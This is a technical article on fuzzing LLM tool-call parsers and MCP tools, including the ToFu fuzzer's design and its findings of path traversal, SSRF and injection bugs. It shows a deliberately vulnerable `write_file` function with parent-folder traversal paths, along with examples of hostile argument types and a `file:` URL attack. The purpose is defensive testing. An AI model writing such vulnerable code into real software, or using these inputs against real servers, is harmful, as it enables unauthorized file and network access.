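| Markup | Repeat `overwrite`, or remove a closing marker | Division into arguments |
| Schema | Declare `text` as an array, or remove its type | Type conversion |

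Fuzzing the schema is easy to forget because the schema isn't part of the model's output. But a fuzzer that declared every argument as a string would never have found the `eval` flaw in vLLM's first Qwen3-Coder parser.

Each run should happen in a separate process so that a crash or an endless loop doesn't also stop the fuzzer. Crucible's *Specialized Harnesses*, the documentation for a set of fuzzing harnesses for machine-learning software, gives example limits of 10 seconds per run and 65,536 bytes per input for text inputs such as schemas.

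When a run fails, the fuzzer shrinks the input by removing parts as long as the failure remains. A 3,000-character report that breaks the parser might shrink to a call whose `text` is just `</arg>`, which makes the cause obvious. The shrunk input then goes into the ordinary test suite, where it runs after every change to the code.

### Seven properties

A fuzzer that checks only for crashes can miss many bugs. In *A First Look at Bugs in LLM Inference Engines*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2025) classified 929 bugs in five programs that run models, including vLLM and llama.cpp, and found that more than 35% had symptoms other than a crash.

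Property-based testing checks a rule that should hold for every input. *A Multi-Domain Study on the Effectiveness of LLMs at Writing Property-Based Tests* (Naziri, Qin and colleagues, 2026) writes such a test as ∀*x*: pre(*x*) ⇒ *P*(*x*, *f*(*x*)), where *f* is the program, *P* is the property and pre(*x*) means that *x* is a valid input. In most programs, a failure on an invalid input is a false alarm. A converter must also handle hostile output, so its no-crash rule has to hold for every string.

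Let *s* be a model's output. The converter either returns a documented error or divides *s* into visible text and tool calls. Let enc(*C*) be the text a model should write to make the call *C*.

| Property | Exact condition | Flaws it catches |
|---|---|---|
| No crash or code execution | For every *s*, the converter returns a result or a documented error. It runs no part of *s* as code, starts no program and opens no file. | llama.cpp's unhandled error; `eval` in vLLM and Xinference |
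| Near-linear time | Doubling the length of *s* roughly doubles the running time, up to the longest output allowed. | vLLM's backtracking search pattern |
| Same result for every splitting | If *p*₁, …, *p*ₖ join to form *s*, streaming them gives the same text and calls as parsing *s* whole. | Text lost after a marker; a repeated `overwrite` that resolves differently in the two modes |
| Round trip | For every call *C* that the schema allows, parsing enc(*C*) returns exactly *C*. | A closing marker inside `text`; the word "null" turned into `None`; rounded identifiers |
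| No invented calls | If *s* contains no opening marker, there are no calls and the visible text is *s*. | Ordinary text mistaken for a call; a harmless `<cat>` that never reaches the user |
| No leaked markup | If *t* and *u* contain no markers, parsing *t* + enc(*C*) + *u* gives the visible text *t* + *u*. | Pieces of markers in the chat window; calls left in the reasoning |
| Schema fit | Every accepted call names a tool on the list, and its arguments pass a strict schema check. | `overwrite` sent as the string `"false"` |

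A fuzzer can detect code execution without generating a working attack. Python's audit hooks can notify a test harness whenever `eval` runs code. With such a hook in place, even a harmless array such as `[1, 2]` would have exposed vLLM's flaw on the first run.

A time limit is a weak test of running time. With a 10-second limit, vLLM's old search pattern would have failed on an 86-character string but passed on a 70-character one. A better test is to repeat a fragment of the input 10, 20, 40 and 80 times and compare the timings. Once the input is long enough to give measurable timings, each doubling makes linear code take about twice as long and quadratic code about four times as long.

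The round trip needs an encoder. The model's prompt template can often serve as one, because it already has to write earlier calls back into the conversation in the model's notation. The round-trip property also prevents a converter from passing by rejecting everything. One of the tests in Naziri and colleagues' study lacks this safeguard because it discards every database query that the server rejects, so it can't detect a server that wrongly rejects a valid query.

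Some round-trip failures can't be fixed in the parser. If a notation has no way to escape its closing marker, two different calls can have the same encoding, and no parser can determine which one was encoded. The fix is to use a different notation or to reject any call that contains a marker in an unexpected place.

Other properties depend on the developers' decisions. Some parsers remove spaces around a call, so the test for leaked markup has to allow for that. The rule about invented calls doesn't fit the Llama 3.2 notation, which has no opening marker, so the tester first has to define which strings count as calls. NVIDIA's parsers deliberately let calls to unknown tools through for later code to reject, so the test for schema fit should run after that check.

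The seven properties still miss some dangerous behavior. A parser that turns the text `yes` into false still returns a proper Boolean, and the round-trip test never includes `yes` because no correct encoder would write it. A parser that completes a truncated call can also pass every test, even if the completed call replaces a long report with its first half.

The fuzzer can find both by encoding the accepted call again and comparing the result with the original output. The false value comes back as `false` instead of `yes`, and the repaired call has a closing quotation mark that the original output lacked. This check also flags harmless differences, such as `True` and `true`, so it is better to have a person review its failures.

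Truncation deserves its own test because testing it takes little compute. A 60-character call can break off in only 59 places, and the fuzzer can try them all. At each one, the converter should return no call unless every possible continuation would produce the same call.

### How many ways to split 60 characters

Here is a call to a tool that reads a file, in the simplified XML-like notation:

```xml
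<call tool="read_file"><arg name="path">log.txt</arg></call>
```

A 60-character output has 59 gaps between characters. A stream may or may not divide at each gap, so there are 2⁵⁹, or about 576 quadrillion, ways to split it. If each run takes a tenth of a millisecond, testing them all would take about 1.8 million years.

Most of them are unnecessary. There are 59 splittings with exactly one cut and 59 × 58 / 2 = 1,711 with exactly two. Together with the uncut output, that makes 1,771 runs, which take less than a fifth of a second. This function generates them:

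```python
from itertools import combinations

def small_splittings(text):
    gaps = range(1, len(text))
    for number_of_cuts in (0, 1, 2):
        for cuts in combinations(gaps, number_of_cuts):
            ends = [0, *cuts, len(text)]
            yield [text[a:b] for a, b in zip(ends, ends[1:])]
```

Two cuts are enough to isolate any stretch of the output in one piece. Trying every pair of cuts covers every way to split a marker across two or three pieces, and every piece that contains the end of one marker and the start of the next. The first run, which has no cuts, would have exposed Poolside's bug, in which parsers dropped whatever followed a marker in the same piece.

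Some bugs appear only with more cuts, such as when a marker arrives in four pieces. Testing all 32,509 splittings with three cuts takes about three seconds. The fuzzer should also deliver the output one character at a time, and then test a random sample of the remaining splittings.

A good sampler varies the probability of cutting each gap from run to run. A fixed probability of one half makes all 2⁵⁹ splittings equally likely, but most of the pieces are then only one or two characters long. The opening marker in the example has 23 characters, so it arrives in one piece only if all 22 gaps inside it stay uncut, which happens about once in 4.2 million runs. With a cut probability of one in ten, it arrives whole in about 10% of runs.

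The number of runs grows quickly with the length of the output. A 4,000-character output has almost eight million splittings with two cuts, so this test works better with short seeds. If the parser reads token numbers instead of text, the stream can divide only between tokens. A 20-token output has 2¹⁹ = 524,288 splittings with any number of cuts, few enough to test them all.

A test harness that reads the arguments with Python's standard JSON parser may miss a difference between the two modes, because the parser keeps only the last value of a repeated name. The harness should also compare the raw argument text, or reject repeated names.

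*Lab 16-01 — Tool-Call Parsing*, an exercise from a course on vLLM, has students check this property by splitting one text in 50 random ways. It suggests an extension with string values that contain the closing marker, which break the exercise's own parser. Models learn in training not to write such values, but the exercise describes this as a contract that is "social, not technical", and an attacker has no reason to respect it.

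### The fixed test suites that projects use

In the largest public collections of parser tests, a person or an AI system chose each input and its expected result in advance. These fixed suites check known cases on every change but don't search for new ones.

vLLM's developers had left eight of its parsers without any tests until late 2025. Browning (2025), in *Add common tool call parser test suite*, proposed a shared set for them, with sample outputs that the coding agent Claude Code helped to write. Of the 140 tests, 99 passed and 41 failed. Browning marked the 41 as expected failures and described each as a parser bug to track down. They were very unevenly spread. The parser for Phi-4-mini failed 10 of its 17 tests and the one for DeepSeek-V3 failed one of 17.

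The shared tests cover different data types and compare streamed output with the original call, so they test examples of two of the properties above. But the suite exempts XML-based parsers from the type check because they return only strings. This exemption hides the error in which the string `"false"` counts as true.

In March 2026, Browning and Claude Code reviewed vLLM's parser fixes since September 2025 and found that several had no tests. Browning (2026) proposed the missing tests in *Add 20 regression tests for 11 tool parser bug fixes*. With them, the parser suite had 510 passing tests, one skipped test and 42 expected failures. All 20 new tests passed, as expected, because the bugs were already fixed. Two of the 11 fixes concerned pieces that varied in size or contained several tokens, which the splitting property covers directly. Another fixed a crash on malformed XML that even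 simple mutation might have found.

Comparing two test suites can reveal gaps in both. zhongdaor-nv sorted 493 vLLM tests, 244 of them for streaming, into NVIDIA's categories for Dynamo. The largest gap was the format of newer Mistral models, which write the tool's name before its arguments. vLLM had many tests for this format, but Dynamo's parser supported only the older notation. Fuzzing Dynamo's parser from its own seeds would probably have missed this, because those seeds would also have been in the older notation.

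NVIDIA's Conformance Corpus, the test cases published with its parsing rules, goes further toward a common standard. It pairs outputs in each model's notation with expected results and repeats the same behavioral cases across model families, including GPT-OSS, Muse Spark and Nemotron 3. To support a new model, a developer adapts these cases to the model's notation, a person reviews them, and an AI agent then writes a parser that passes them.

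The corpus can specify behavior that general properties leave open, such as how much of a broken answer to keep. But it is a fixed suite, and an agent that can see all the tests may write a parser that handles little else. Fuzzing, with the corpus as seeds, would be a useful independent check.

### Comparing providers, and what went wrong with Kimi K2

Anyone can serve Moonshot AI's Kimi models, and the same model may call tools less reliably with one provider than with another. Moonshot AI's *K2-Vendor-Verifier Now Includes "Kimi K2 Thinking"* (2025) describes a public benchmark that tests whole deployments so that users can compare providers. It mainly measures whether a provider's copy of the model calls tools when it should, and what share of its calls parse and match the schema (schema accuracy). This resembles differential testing because every provider gets the same requests, but it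 isn't fuzzing because those requests are fixed.

vLLM's *Chasing 100% Accuracy* shows what such a comparison can uncover. On about 4,000 requests, Moonshot's own service made 1,286 tool calls, all of them valid. When the post's author ran the model on vLLM 0.11.0, it made only 248 calls, of which 218 were valid. The post traces the difference to three causes:

- vLLM left out the part of the prompt that tells the model to begin its answer. For security, it passed only explicitly declared settings to the model's prompt template, and this setting was not declared. The model often continued the conversation as plain text.
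- vLLM converted empty messages into lists. The template expected a string, so it wrote the list's Python notation into the prompt.
- The parser expected every call's identifier to look like `functions.search:2`. If the model wrote `search:2`, the code looked for text after a dot that wasn't there, raised an error and discarded the call.

Fuzzing the converter could have found only the last of these three faults. Deleting `functions.` from a recorded output is an ordinary markup mutation, and the resulting error would have violated the first property. The other two faults were in the code that builds the prompt, so even a perfect parser would have received bad output. Such faults are a good reason to test a whole deployment as well.

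After the fixes, the model made 1,325 calls. The post's table lists 1,007 of them as valid, for a schema accuracy of 76%, but its text gives 971. Some of the remaining errors were calls to tools that appeared earlier in the conversation but were not available in the current request. Moonshot's service prevents these errors with constrained decoding, which vLLM did not yet use for this purpose.

Moonshot released a broader test, the Kimi Vendor Verifier, with its K2.6 model. Tool calling is one of its six checks, which also cover image input, long answers and coding. According to Kimi's *Rebuilding the "Chain of Trust"*, a full run takes about 15 hours on two servers with eight graphics processors each. A converter fuzzer could run on an ordinary laptop, so it is practical to use after every code change.

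### Published fuzzing is scarce

No published fuzzing campaign seems to report a bug in a tool-call parser. The closest is Crucible's harness for llama.cpp, which uses libFuzzer to send generated text to the function that extracts tool calls from a model's answer. The harness works with made-up grammars, and according to Crucible's documentation, the templates of real models may use other parts of the parser.

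Crucible has published three findings, all from the code that loads model files in stable-diffusion.cpp, an image generator. The project publishes a bug only after the developers have fixed it, so the tool-call harness may have found bugs that aren't public yet.

llama.cpp also takes part in OSS-Fuzz, a Google service that continuously fuzzes open-source software. A coverage report by Fuzz Introspector (2026) lists six fuzzers for it in January 2026. They cover grammars, chat templates, model files, inference and the translation of schemas into grammars, but not the tool-call parser.

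The schema fuzzer shows how a coverage figure can mislead. It covered 76% of the functions it could reach, but 375 of those functions come from a general JSON library and only six from the translator. A large translator function that processes the schema itself never ran. The fuzzer seems to have mostly tested the JSON library. Generating schemas instead of bytes would avoid this.

Other fuzzers test different parts of the system. In *Continuous Discovery of Vulnerabilities in LLM Serving Systems with Fuzzing*, Zhao, Zhao and colleagues (2026) fuzzed vLLM and SGLang with series of valid requests, varying when they arrived and overlapped. They found 15 potential vulnerabilities, of which developers confirmed 10. In one, data left over from one user's request changed the answer to another's. These flaws are serious, but they concern shared memory and scheduling. Ananto and colleagues start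 after the converter, with calls that already fit the schema.

The property-based tests in Naziri and colleagues' study may be the nearest thing to a search for new parser bugs. Naziri and colleagues used Agentic-PBT, a prompt that has a coding agent read a program, propose properties, write tests and run them. They applied it to ten programs, including vLLM and SGLang, and one of the tests checked that streaming did not change a response. They tested 30 randomly chosen features of each program, out of 4,399 for vLLM, so the tests would have covered the tool parsers only by chance.

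### Do models that read code replace fuzzing?

An AI system that reads code can recognize an `eval` call without running it. If these systems find most bugs, building a fuzzer may not be worth the effort.

The best direct comparison comes from Project Zero, Google's team for finding security flaws. Groß (2026), in *Fuzzers vs. AI*, compared two tools that Google runs on V8, the JavaScript engine in the Chrome browser. Fuzzilli is a fuzzer that generates JavaScript programs. BigSleep is an AI system that reviews new code every day and writes a test case for each bug it finds. The results for April to September 2026 depend heavily on what counts as a finding:

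| What counts | BigSleep | Fuzzilli |
|---|---|---|
| All bug reports | 441 | 316 |
| Reports classed as vulnerabilities | 95 | 178 |
| Vulnerabilities that were not duplicates or intended behavior and led to a fix | 45 | 37 |

The last row is the fairest measure, and Groß calls it roughly a tie. Only 25% of the specific bugs overlapped. That method tends to underestimate the overlap, so Project Zero also ran experiments on vulnerabilities reported since 2023 and found an overlap of about 60%. Either way, each tool found many bugs that the other missed, and Groß recommends using both.

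These numbers may not hold for converters. V8 is a huge program with complicated bugs, and Google has fuzzed it for years with a purpose-built tool. A tool-call parser may be only a few hundred lines long, so a model can read all of it, and nobody has built a comparable fuzzer for one. These differences could put the AI system further ahead. But a parser's input is short and has a simple structure, which suits a fuzzer. Groß also doesn't compare costs, because Google has not tuned either system for the lowest cost per bug.

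The kind of bug probably matters more than the totals. `eval` is easy to spot in the code, but a parser that fails when a marker arrives in three pieces can look reasonable. A fuzzer finds that parser bug in a fraction of a second. BigSleep's daily review looks at new changes to V8's code, and a similar reviewer could miss a parser bug that appears when an outside library changes how it decodes special tokens. Rerunning the saved tests might catch it.

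Studies of other software also found that the methods complement each other. Naziri and colleagues tested two C compilers and found 23 crashes with MetaMut, a specialized fuzzer, and four different ones with Agentic-PBT. Most of the bugs Agentic-PBT found were wrong results, which a fuzzer that only looks for crashes would miss. Team Atlanta's *More CPUs Won't Find More Bugs* describes Gondar, which combines AI agents with the Java fuzzer Jazzer. Gondar exploited 35 of the 46 vulnerabilities that Jazzer missed by itself.

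A practical approach is to have a model write the harness, the encoder and the properties for each parser, and let a fuzzer supply the inputs. With Claude Opus 5, Agentic-PBT wrote 202 tests for vLLM for $62.50. Developers had confirmed 65 new bugs across all ten programs by the time of the study. But when Naziri and colleagues checked 30 randomly chosen failures, only nine were real bugs. In many of the others, the test expected behavior that the program had never guaranteed. For a converter, the seven properties would define much of the expected behavior in advance, but someone would still have to decide what the parser should do with a broken call.

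## Fuzzing tools with valid but hostile arguments

After the conversion and the schema check, a tool receives its arguments as ordinary values. To fuzz the tool, a tester calls it with values that fit the schema but that an attacker might choose, then checks what the tool does with them.

### What a type leaves out

Most dangerous arguments are strings. An example tool in the Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) specification takes two strings, `region` and `query`. Only their descriptions distinguish the name of a region from a query that a database will execute.

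Each kind of string goes to a different interpreter, and each interpreter has its own dangerous values:

| Argument | What interprets it | A harmful value of the right type |
|---|---|---|
| File path | The file system | A path that leads out of the permitted folder |
| Web address | A browser or network library | An address on the server's private network |
| Database query | The database | A deletion, in a tool meant only for searching |
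| Shell command | The shell | A file name with a character that starts a second command |

A simple version of `write_file` has this problem:

```python
PROJECT = Path("/home/ana/project").resolve()

def write_file(path, text, overwrite):
    target = PROJECT / path
    with open(target, "w" if overwrite else "x") as file:
        file.write(text)
```

With the path `notes/today.txt`, the function writes inside the project folder. With `../private/today.txt`, the two dots lead to the parent folder, so the function writes to `/home/ana/private/today.txt`. An absolute path can also lead outside the project folder, because Python discards that folder when it joins the two. Both kinds of hostile path fit the schema, and the tool reports success.

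Two changes before the `open` call prevent this:

```python
    target = (PROJECT / path).resolve()
    if not target.is_relative_to(PROJECT):
        raise ValueError("path is outside the project folder")
```

`resolve` finds the path's real location, following any symbolic links, and `is_relative_to` compares whole folder names. A small gap remains because another program could replace a folder with a link between the check and the write.

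Anthropic's Filesystem MCP server is a real counterpart to `write_file`. It checked its paths, but Beber's *EscapeRoute* describes two mistakes in the check. One was that the server accepted any path that began with the name of a permitted folder. If that folder was `/home/ana/project`, it also accepted files in `/home/ana/project-private`. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-53110* (2025) rates the severity of this flaw at 7.3 out of 10 and lists 0.6.4 and 2025.7.01 as the fixed versions.

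The other flaw, CVE-2025-53109, involved symbolic links. The server checked where each link led and raised an error if that was outside the permitted folders. But an error handler meant for new files, which have no real location yet, caught this error too. The handler checked only the folder that contained the link and let the operation continue, so the server could read or write any file that the user account it ran under could. A fuzzer could find this flaw only if its test folder contained such a link, because a path string can't create one.

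Arguments passed to a shell cause similar trouble. *Unicode TAG-Block Concealment of Tool-Metadata Payloads in the Model Context Protocol* (2026) reports that the ios-simulator-mcp server passed an argument to a shell without sanitizing it (CVE-2025-52573). The usual fix is to start the program directly with a list of arguments, so that no shell interprets them. Filtering the text is less reliable. Adversa AI surveyed 11 open-source agents in 2026 and found that the command filters of 10 could let through commands that the shell interpreted differently from the filter, according to SC Media's *Shell injection flaw found in 10 of 11 open-source AI agents* (2026).

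The US National Security Agency's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) advises developers to check inputs against the schema, the expected ranges and the context in which a program will use them. A fuzzer also needs information about that context to select test values and identify failures.

### How ToFu builds a test from a description

ToFu, the fuzzer that Ananto and colleagues built, gets this information from the descriptions that tools already provide for language models. It tests each tool in five steps:

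1. ToFu reads the tool's name, description and schema and puts them in a common format.
2. A language model, GPT-4.1, compares the arguments with a list of security checks and selects those that apply.
3. The model writes about 11 starting calls aimed at the selected checks, adapting hostile values from a fixed collection.
4. Atheris, a fuzzer for Python that uses coverage feedback, alters the arguments and calls the tool repeatedly.
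5. After each call, the checks examine what happened, and ToFu saves any input that caused a violation.

ToFu has 74 checks, which Ananto and colleagues call sanitizers. Most are based on types of weakness in the CWE catalogue. Each check has four parts, shown here for a check on file paths:

| Part | Content |
|---|---|
| When it applies | Arguments with names such as `path`, `file` or `dir` |
| Hostile values to try | Parent-folder references, absolute paths and encoded versions of both |
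| Security property | Every file the tool opens is inside the permitted folder |
| Evidence needed | The paths that the tool passes to the operating system |

The permitted folder comes from the tester's configuration, because a description such as "the project folder" doesn't give its location.

Eleven checks run on every call, 35 run whenever the relevant evidence appears, and 27 run only if the model selects them. One more check is on the list but never runs. The model selected about three checks per tool on average and none for 193 tools.

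Atheris normally produces bytes, so ToFu uses the schema to decode them into arguments, including nested objects and arrays. When an argument has a fixed list of choices, ToFu picks from that list. Ananto and colleagues describe the inputs as schema-valid, but they also instruct the model to generate a few values of the wrong type.

Some tools need a whole file as input. The model can call small programs that create valid PDFs, spreadsheets, archives and other documents, and it did so for 119 tools.

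*Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) describes Corvus, a program that sends attack values from a fixed collection to every tool an internet-facing server offers. Corvus doesn't need the server's code, but it doesn't derive a separate rule for each tool from the tool's description.

### Two rules for recognizing a violation

Besides watching for crashes, ToFu has two other oracles.

The observation rule depends on watching the tool at its sinks, the operations where a bad value does damage, such as opening a file or starting a program. ToFu has 21 tracers that intercept the Python functions for these operations and record each use. For a check *S*, tool *T* and input *x*, let τ(*T*, *x*) be the recorded events:

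```
violation if an event in τ(T, x) breaks the property of S
```

ToFu checks paths by finding the real location of each opened file and of the permitted folder, then testing whether the file is inside the folder. The result doesn't depend on how the input disguised the path or whether the tool returned an error.

The tracers work only when the tool runs inside the fuzzer's own Python process. For JavaScript servers and other tools that ToFu can't look inside, it uses an outcome rule. Let *V*(*x*) mean that a check considers *x* forbidden:

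```
violation if V(x) and the tool did not reject x
```

What counts as rejection depends on the tool. A tool that extracts JSON from arbitrary text should accept almost anything, while `write_file` should refuse a path outside its folder. For each outcome check, GPT-4.1 therefore chooses one of three settings:

| Setting | When ToFu reports a violation |
|---|---|
| The tool must raise an error | The tool returns successfully |
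| The tool may return a safe substitute, such as an empty list | The tool returns anything else |
| The tool may accept any input | Never |

The outcome rule can produce false alarms. Suppose `write_file` removed the two dots from a path and saved the file safely inside the project folder. Under the first setting, ToFu would still report a violation because the call succeeded.

Fixed code, not the language model, determines whether a run has failed, so the same evidence always gives the same verdict. The model is not given the fuzzing results, but it still influences the verdict through its choice of checks and settings. If it wrongly classifies a tool as allowed to accept any input, ToFu will not report a real flaw that only the outcome rule could detect.

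Adding security detectors to a fuzzer is an older idea. The jug.ch slides *Fuzzing Java with Jazzer* (2022) argue that fuzzers already explore code well but need a way to detect vulnerabilities when they occur. Jazzer had detectors for command injection and unsafe deserialization, among others. ToFu adds rules that differ between tools. For example, writing outside the project folder is a violation for `write_file` but would be normal for a general backup tool.

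### A screenshot tool that reads local files

One of ToFu's reports concerned a JavaScript server with a tool that screenshots web pages. The tool's `url` argument was a string described as "The URL of the webpage to screenshot", and the server checked only that the string was a valid URL.

GPT-4.1 selected eight checks for this argument and specified that the tool should raise an error if any failed. It then generated nine starting calls, including some with addresses on the server's own machine and one with a `file:` address, which names a local file instead of a web page.

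The tool passed the `file:` address to its browser and returned a screenshot of the file and a success message. ToFu had no tracer in the JavaScript process, so it detected the flaw through the outcome rule. Ananto and colleagues repeated the call by hand and found that the tool would show any file the server's user could read and also list the contents of folders.

Nothing crashed, and no schema type distinguishes a web page from a local file, so the only sign of a violation was the word "webpage" in the description. The developers could fix the tool by accepting only `http` and `https` addresses and blocking connections to private networks, including those reached through a redirect.

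### From 13,875 records to 253 bugs

Ananto and colleagues started with MCPCorpus, a public dataset of MCP projects. Most of its records dropped out before the main evaluation:

| Stage | Remaining |
|---|---|
| Records in the dataset | 13,875 |
| Active GitHub repositories with at least ten stars, without duplicates or clients | 2,222 |
| Written in Python or JavaScript | 1,847 |
| At least one tool found in the code | 1,404 |
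| Installed successfully and listed their tools | 482 |
| Ran at least one tool call | 417 |
| Returned at least one successful result | 273 |

On these 273 servers, ToFu produced 508 candidate bugs. Ananto and colleagues reviewed them by hand, dismissed 103 as harmless and removed 152 duplicates. This left 253 reproducible bugs, affecting 343 tools on 118 servers. The tools outnumber the bugs because several tools can share the same faulty code.

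| Type of bug | Number | What the tool does |
|---|---|---|
| Reflected output | 115 | Returns markup from its input without escaping it |
| Path traversal | 64 | Reads or writes a file outside the permitted folder |
| Log injection | 58 | Writes line breaks from its input into a log, which can create false entries |
| Server-side request forgery | 7 | Connects to an address it should refuse, such as one on a private network |
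| Data exfiltration | 5 | Reads a sensitive file and sends its contents elsewhere |
| Command injection | 3 | Lets an argument change the command that it runs |
| Leftover temporary file | 1 | Fails to delete a temporary file after the call |

Reflected output and log injection make up 173 of the 253 bugs, or 68%, and their effects are often limited. Reflected markup is dangerous if a browser displays it as part of a page, but much less so if only a language model receives it as text. Ananto and colleagues count log injection as low impact if the log contains only error or debugging messages, but they don't report how many of their bugs are low impact.

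The 79 bugs that involve unwanted access to files, networks or commands are more worrying. Path traversal accounts for 64 of them, so developers using ToFu's results should probably start with file tools. The review excluded tools whose purpose is to run commands, so finding only three command injection bugs doesn't show that such flaws are rare among tools.

These figures are also biased as estimates of how common bugs are. ToFu found bugs in 118 of 273 servers (43%), but this rate is biased upwards because the 273 included only servers where at least one tool succeeded on a hostile input, which would exclude a server that correctly rejected them all. Of the 417 servers that ran at least one call, 28% had a verified bug. The rate for tools is biased downwards. About 10% of the 3,405 tools on the 273 servers had a verified bug, but ToFu managed to run only about 1,500 of those tools in later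 full runs.

For *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions*, Shi, Fu and colleagues (2026) searched public vulnerability records, advisories and project issues and found 53 valid reports in 45 MCP servers. ToFu found almost five times as many bugs, though many were of less serious types.

### Five other analyzers on the same servers

Ananto and colleagues ran five other analyzers on the 273 servers. VIPER-MCP and ToolFuzz both use agents to send requests to tools.

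| Analyzer | What it looks for | Servers flagged | Also flagged by ToFu |
|---|---|---|---|
| ToFu | Tools that mishandle hostile arguments | 118 | – |
| ToolFuzz | Tools that fail or give wrong answers when an agent uses them | 92 | 56 |
| VIPER-MCP | Paths through the code from an argument to a sink | 48, with exploits confirmed on 11 | 36, with exploits confirmed on 7 |
| Cisco MCP Scanner | Suspicious descriptions, and code that doesn't match them | 46 | 23 |
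| CodeQL | Known insecure patterns in source code | 95 | 56 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | Flaws that a language model notices when it reviews a tool | 119 | 71 |

The figures in this table can't be used to rank the tools. Manual review reduced ToFu's figure from 147 servers to 118, while the other figures count unreviewed findings. The analyzers also look for different things. CodeQL raised 59 alerts on a server for Google Workspace, but for problems such as passwords in logs and disabled certificate checks. Cisco's scanner often reacts to words that suggest a powerful tool, such as one that sends email.

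General scanners can flag so many servers as risky that their ratings are of little use. *MCP server security scores are review prompts, not verdicts* (Schipper, 2026) cites a study in which existing scanners rated 96.89% of MCP servers as risky, and the researchers judged these ratings unreliable. Schipper's own scanner puts 63% of servers in its lowest risk band.

At least one of the five analyzers also flagged 110 of the 118 servers that ToFu flagged, so only ToFu found the other eight. Together, the analyzers flagged 88 servers that ToFu did not. For about 63% of these, ToFu never tested the tools' main code, because the server failed to start, hung or rejected every input at an early check. Ananto and colleagues also say that about a fifth of the servers found only by static analysis, which reads code without running it, had problems that single calls don't reveal. These include faulty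 cleaning patterns and race conditions like the gap in the repaired `write_file`.

Running a tool with hostile values can confirm flaws that other methods leave uncertain. On a server for the Directus content system, VIPER-MCP found a path from an argument to a network request, but its agent tried only an ordinary public address and did not confirm a flaw. ToFu tried hundreds of hostile addresses and showed that the tool accepted them.

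A model that read the code and a fuzzer found different flaws, as in Google's comparison on V8. Claude Sonnet 5 reported problems on a server that ToFu couldn't log in to, but missed a command injection bug that ToFu found in another server.

### What each part of ToFu contributes

To find out which parts of ToFu matter, Ananto and colleagues removed them one at a time and repeated the tests, with 60 seconds for each tool. They didn't review the results by hand, so these are candidate bugs:

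| Version of ToFu | All candidates | Path traversal | Reflected output and log injection |
|---|---|---|---|
| Complete (average of three runs) | 430 | 101 | 279 |
| Starting calls built without the language model | 396 | 91 | 257 |
| No checks selected by the model | 311 | 0 | 301 |
| No language model at all | 293 | 0 | 289 |
| No starting calls | 244 | 1 | 195 |

The language model helped ToFu mainly by choosing the checks that find more serious bugs. Without the model, ToFu still produced 293 candidates, about two thirds of the original number, but none were path traversal, and 289 were reflected output or log injection, whose checks run with or without the model.

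Starting calls mattered even more to the total. Without them, the fuzzer had to discover useful values by mutation and found only one path traversal candidate. Using ordinary code to fit a fixed collection of hostile values to the schema recovered most of the loss. A project that can't send its tool descriptions to an outside model could use such a collection and have a developer select the checks.

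Skipping the selection and running all 74 checks on every tool didn't slow down the fuzzing, but it more than doubled the number of reports. On tools flagged only when all the checks were run, over 90% of the reports were false.

It also revealed 13 real bugs that the usual version had missed. Five were in one WordPress server written in JavaScript, for which GPT-4.1 had chosen a network check that works only in Python. Including the server's language in the prompt should prevent this error, and a newer model might also choose a better check.

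Removing the tracers cut the number of candidates on Python servers from 169 to 107 in one complete run, but cut the number on JavaScript servers by only one. A tracer for JavaScript would be useful because it could show what a tool did with a forbidden value, not only whether the call succeeded.

### A minute per tool

Running a tool is slower than running a parser. ToFu made about 43 to 46 calls per second. Even so, it found 231 of the 253 verified bugs with a budget of 60 seconds per tool. Longer runs found the other 22, between 111 seconds and 70 minutes after fuzzing of the tool began.

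Only 34 servers received the longer, 24-hour runs, so the other 239 may contain more bugs that take over a minute to find. Ananto and colleagues plotted coverage over time for eight tools. Fuzzing reached new code in five of them after the first minute, but in none after about an hour. It seems reasonable to fuzz briefly after each code change and occasionally for an hour or two.

ToFu's coverage figures leave out some of the software that a tool relies on. For example, if a tool is a thin layer around a browser, ToFu measures coverage of the layer but not of the browser.

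The three complete runs found similar numbers of candidate bugs (436, 428 and 427), but only 342 appeared in all three. Any two runs shared between 75% and 81% of the bugs that either had found. The model's responses were identical each time, so the variation came from the fuzzer's random choices.

If one run finds a bug and the next doesn't, the bug may still be there, so developers should test a fix with the saved input as well as a new run.

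### Tools that damaged the test machine

Fuzzing a tool means carrying out its actions, and four servers affected the machine on which Ananto and colleagues tested them:

- UltimateCoderMCP deleted files outside its workspace.
- obsidian-mcp followed a path out of its folder of notes.
- tmux-mcp closed terminal sessions that it hadn't opened.
- DesktopCommanderMCP kept starting new processes without limit.

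The experiment ran each fuzzer in a sandbox, a restricted environment in which most of the file system was read-only and temporary files were private. A read-only file system protects against the first problem. To protect against the last two, the sandbox also has to hide other processes and limit how many the tool can start.

A fuzzer with network access and real credentials could send thousands of emails or delete customer data from a production database. Testers should give tools throwaway accounts and mock services instead. The NSA recommends similar isolation in normal use and advises treating every tool execution as potentially high-risk.

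### Missing logins and backends

Many tools also do little without an account, and isolation makes this problem worse. ToFu ran all 123 tools on a server for the Sitecore content system, but only one ever succeeded and the others failed at login. Only one tool worked on the Google Workspace server, too. When a fuzzer finds no bugs on such a server, testers learn almost nothing about the code behind the login.

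Test accounts would help with hosted services, but they take time to set up and may have usage limits. Mock backends are faster and safer, but they must behave realistically enough for the tool to continue, and they may not expose bugs that depend on the real service.

### Bugs that need several calls

ToFu tests one call at a time, but some bugs need a sequence of calls. Suppose the server that offers `write_file` also has a tool for unpacking archives. One call could unpack a symbolic link into the project folder, and a second could write through that link to a file outside the folder. A fuzzer that tests `write_file` alone, in a folder without links, would not find this bug.

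Sequences of calls also matter for access control. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) has no built-in sessions, so its *Tools* specification suggests that a server return an identifier, called a handle, which the model includes in later calls. A shopping tool might create a basket and return the handle `bsk_a1b2c3`, which another tool needs to add an item. MCP advises servers with user accounts to check on every call that the caller is allowed to use the handle.

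To test this rule, a fuzzer has to create a basket as one user and try to change it as another. If it only invents handles, the server will reject them as unknown and the access check may never run. Ananto and colleagues suggest building such sequences automatically by matching the outputs of some tools with the arguments of others. The number of possible sequences grows quickly, though, and they leave this to future work.

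### When a tool is doing its job

VIPER-MCP confirmed four exploits on servers where ToFu reported nothing, all involving tools whose purpose is to run code or commands. In one case, VIPER-MCP's agent used a tool for AppleScript, Apple's automation language, to read a system file. ToFu had called the same tool successfully more than 2,000 times without raising an alert, because the tool is supposed to run scripts.

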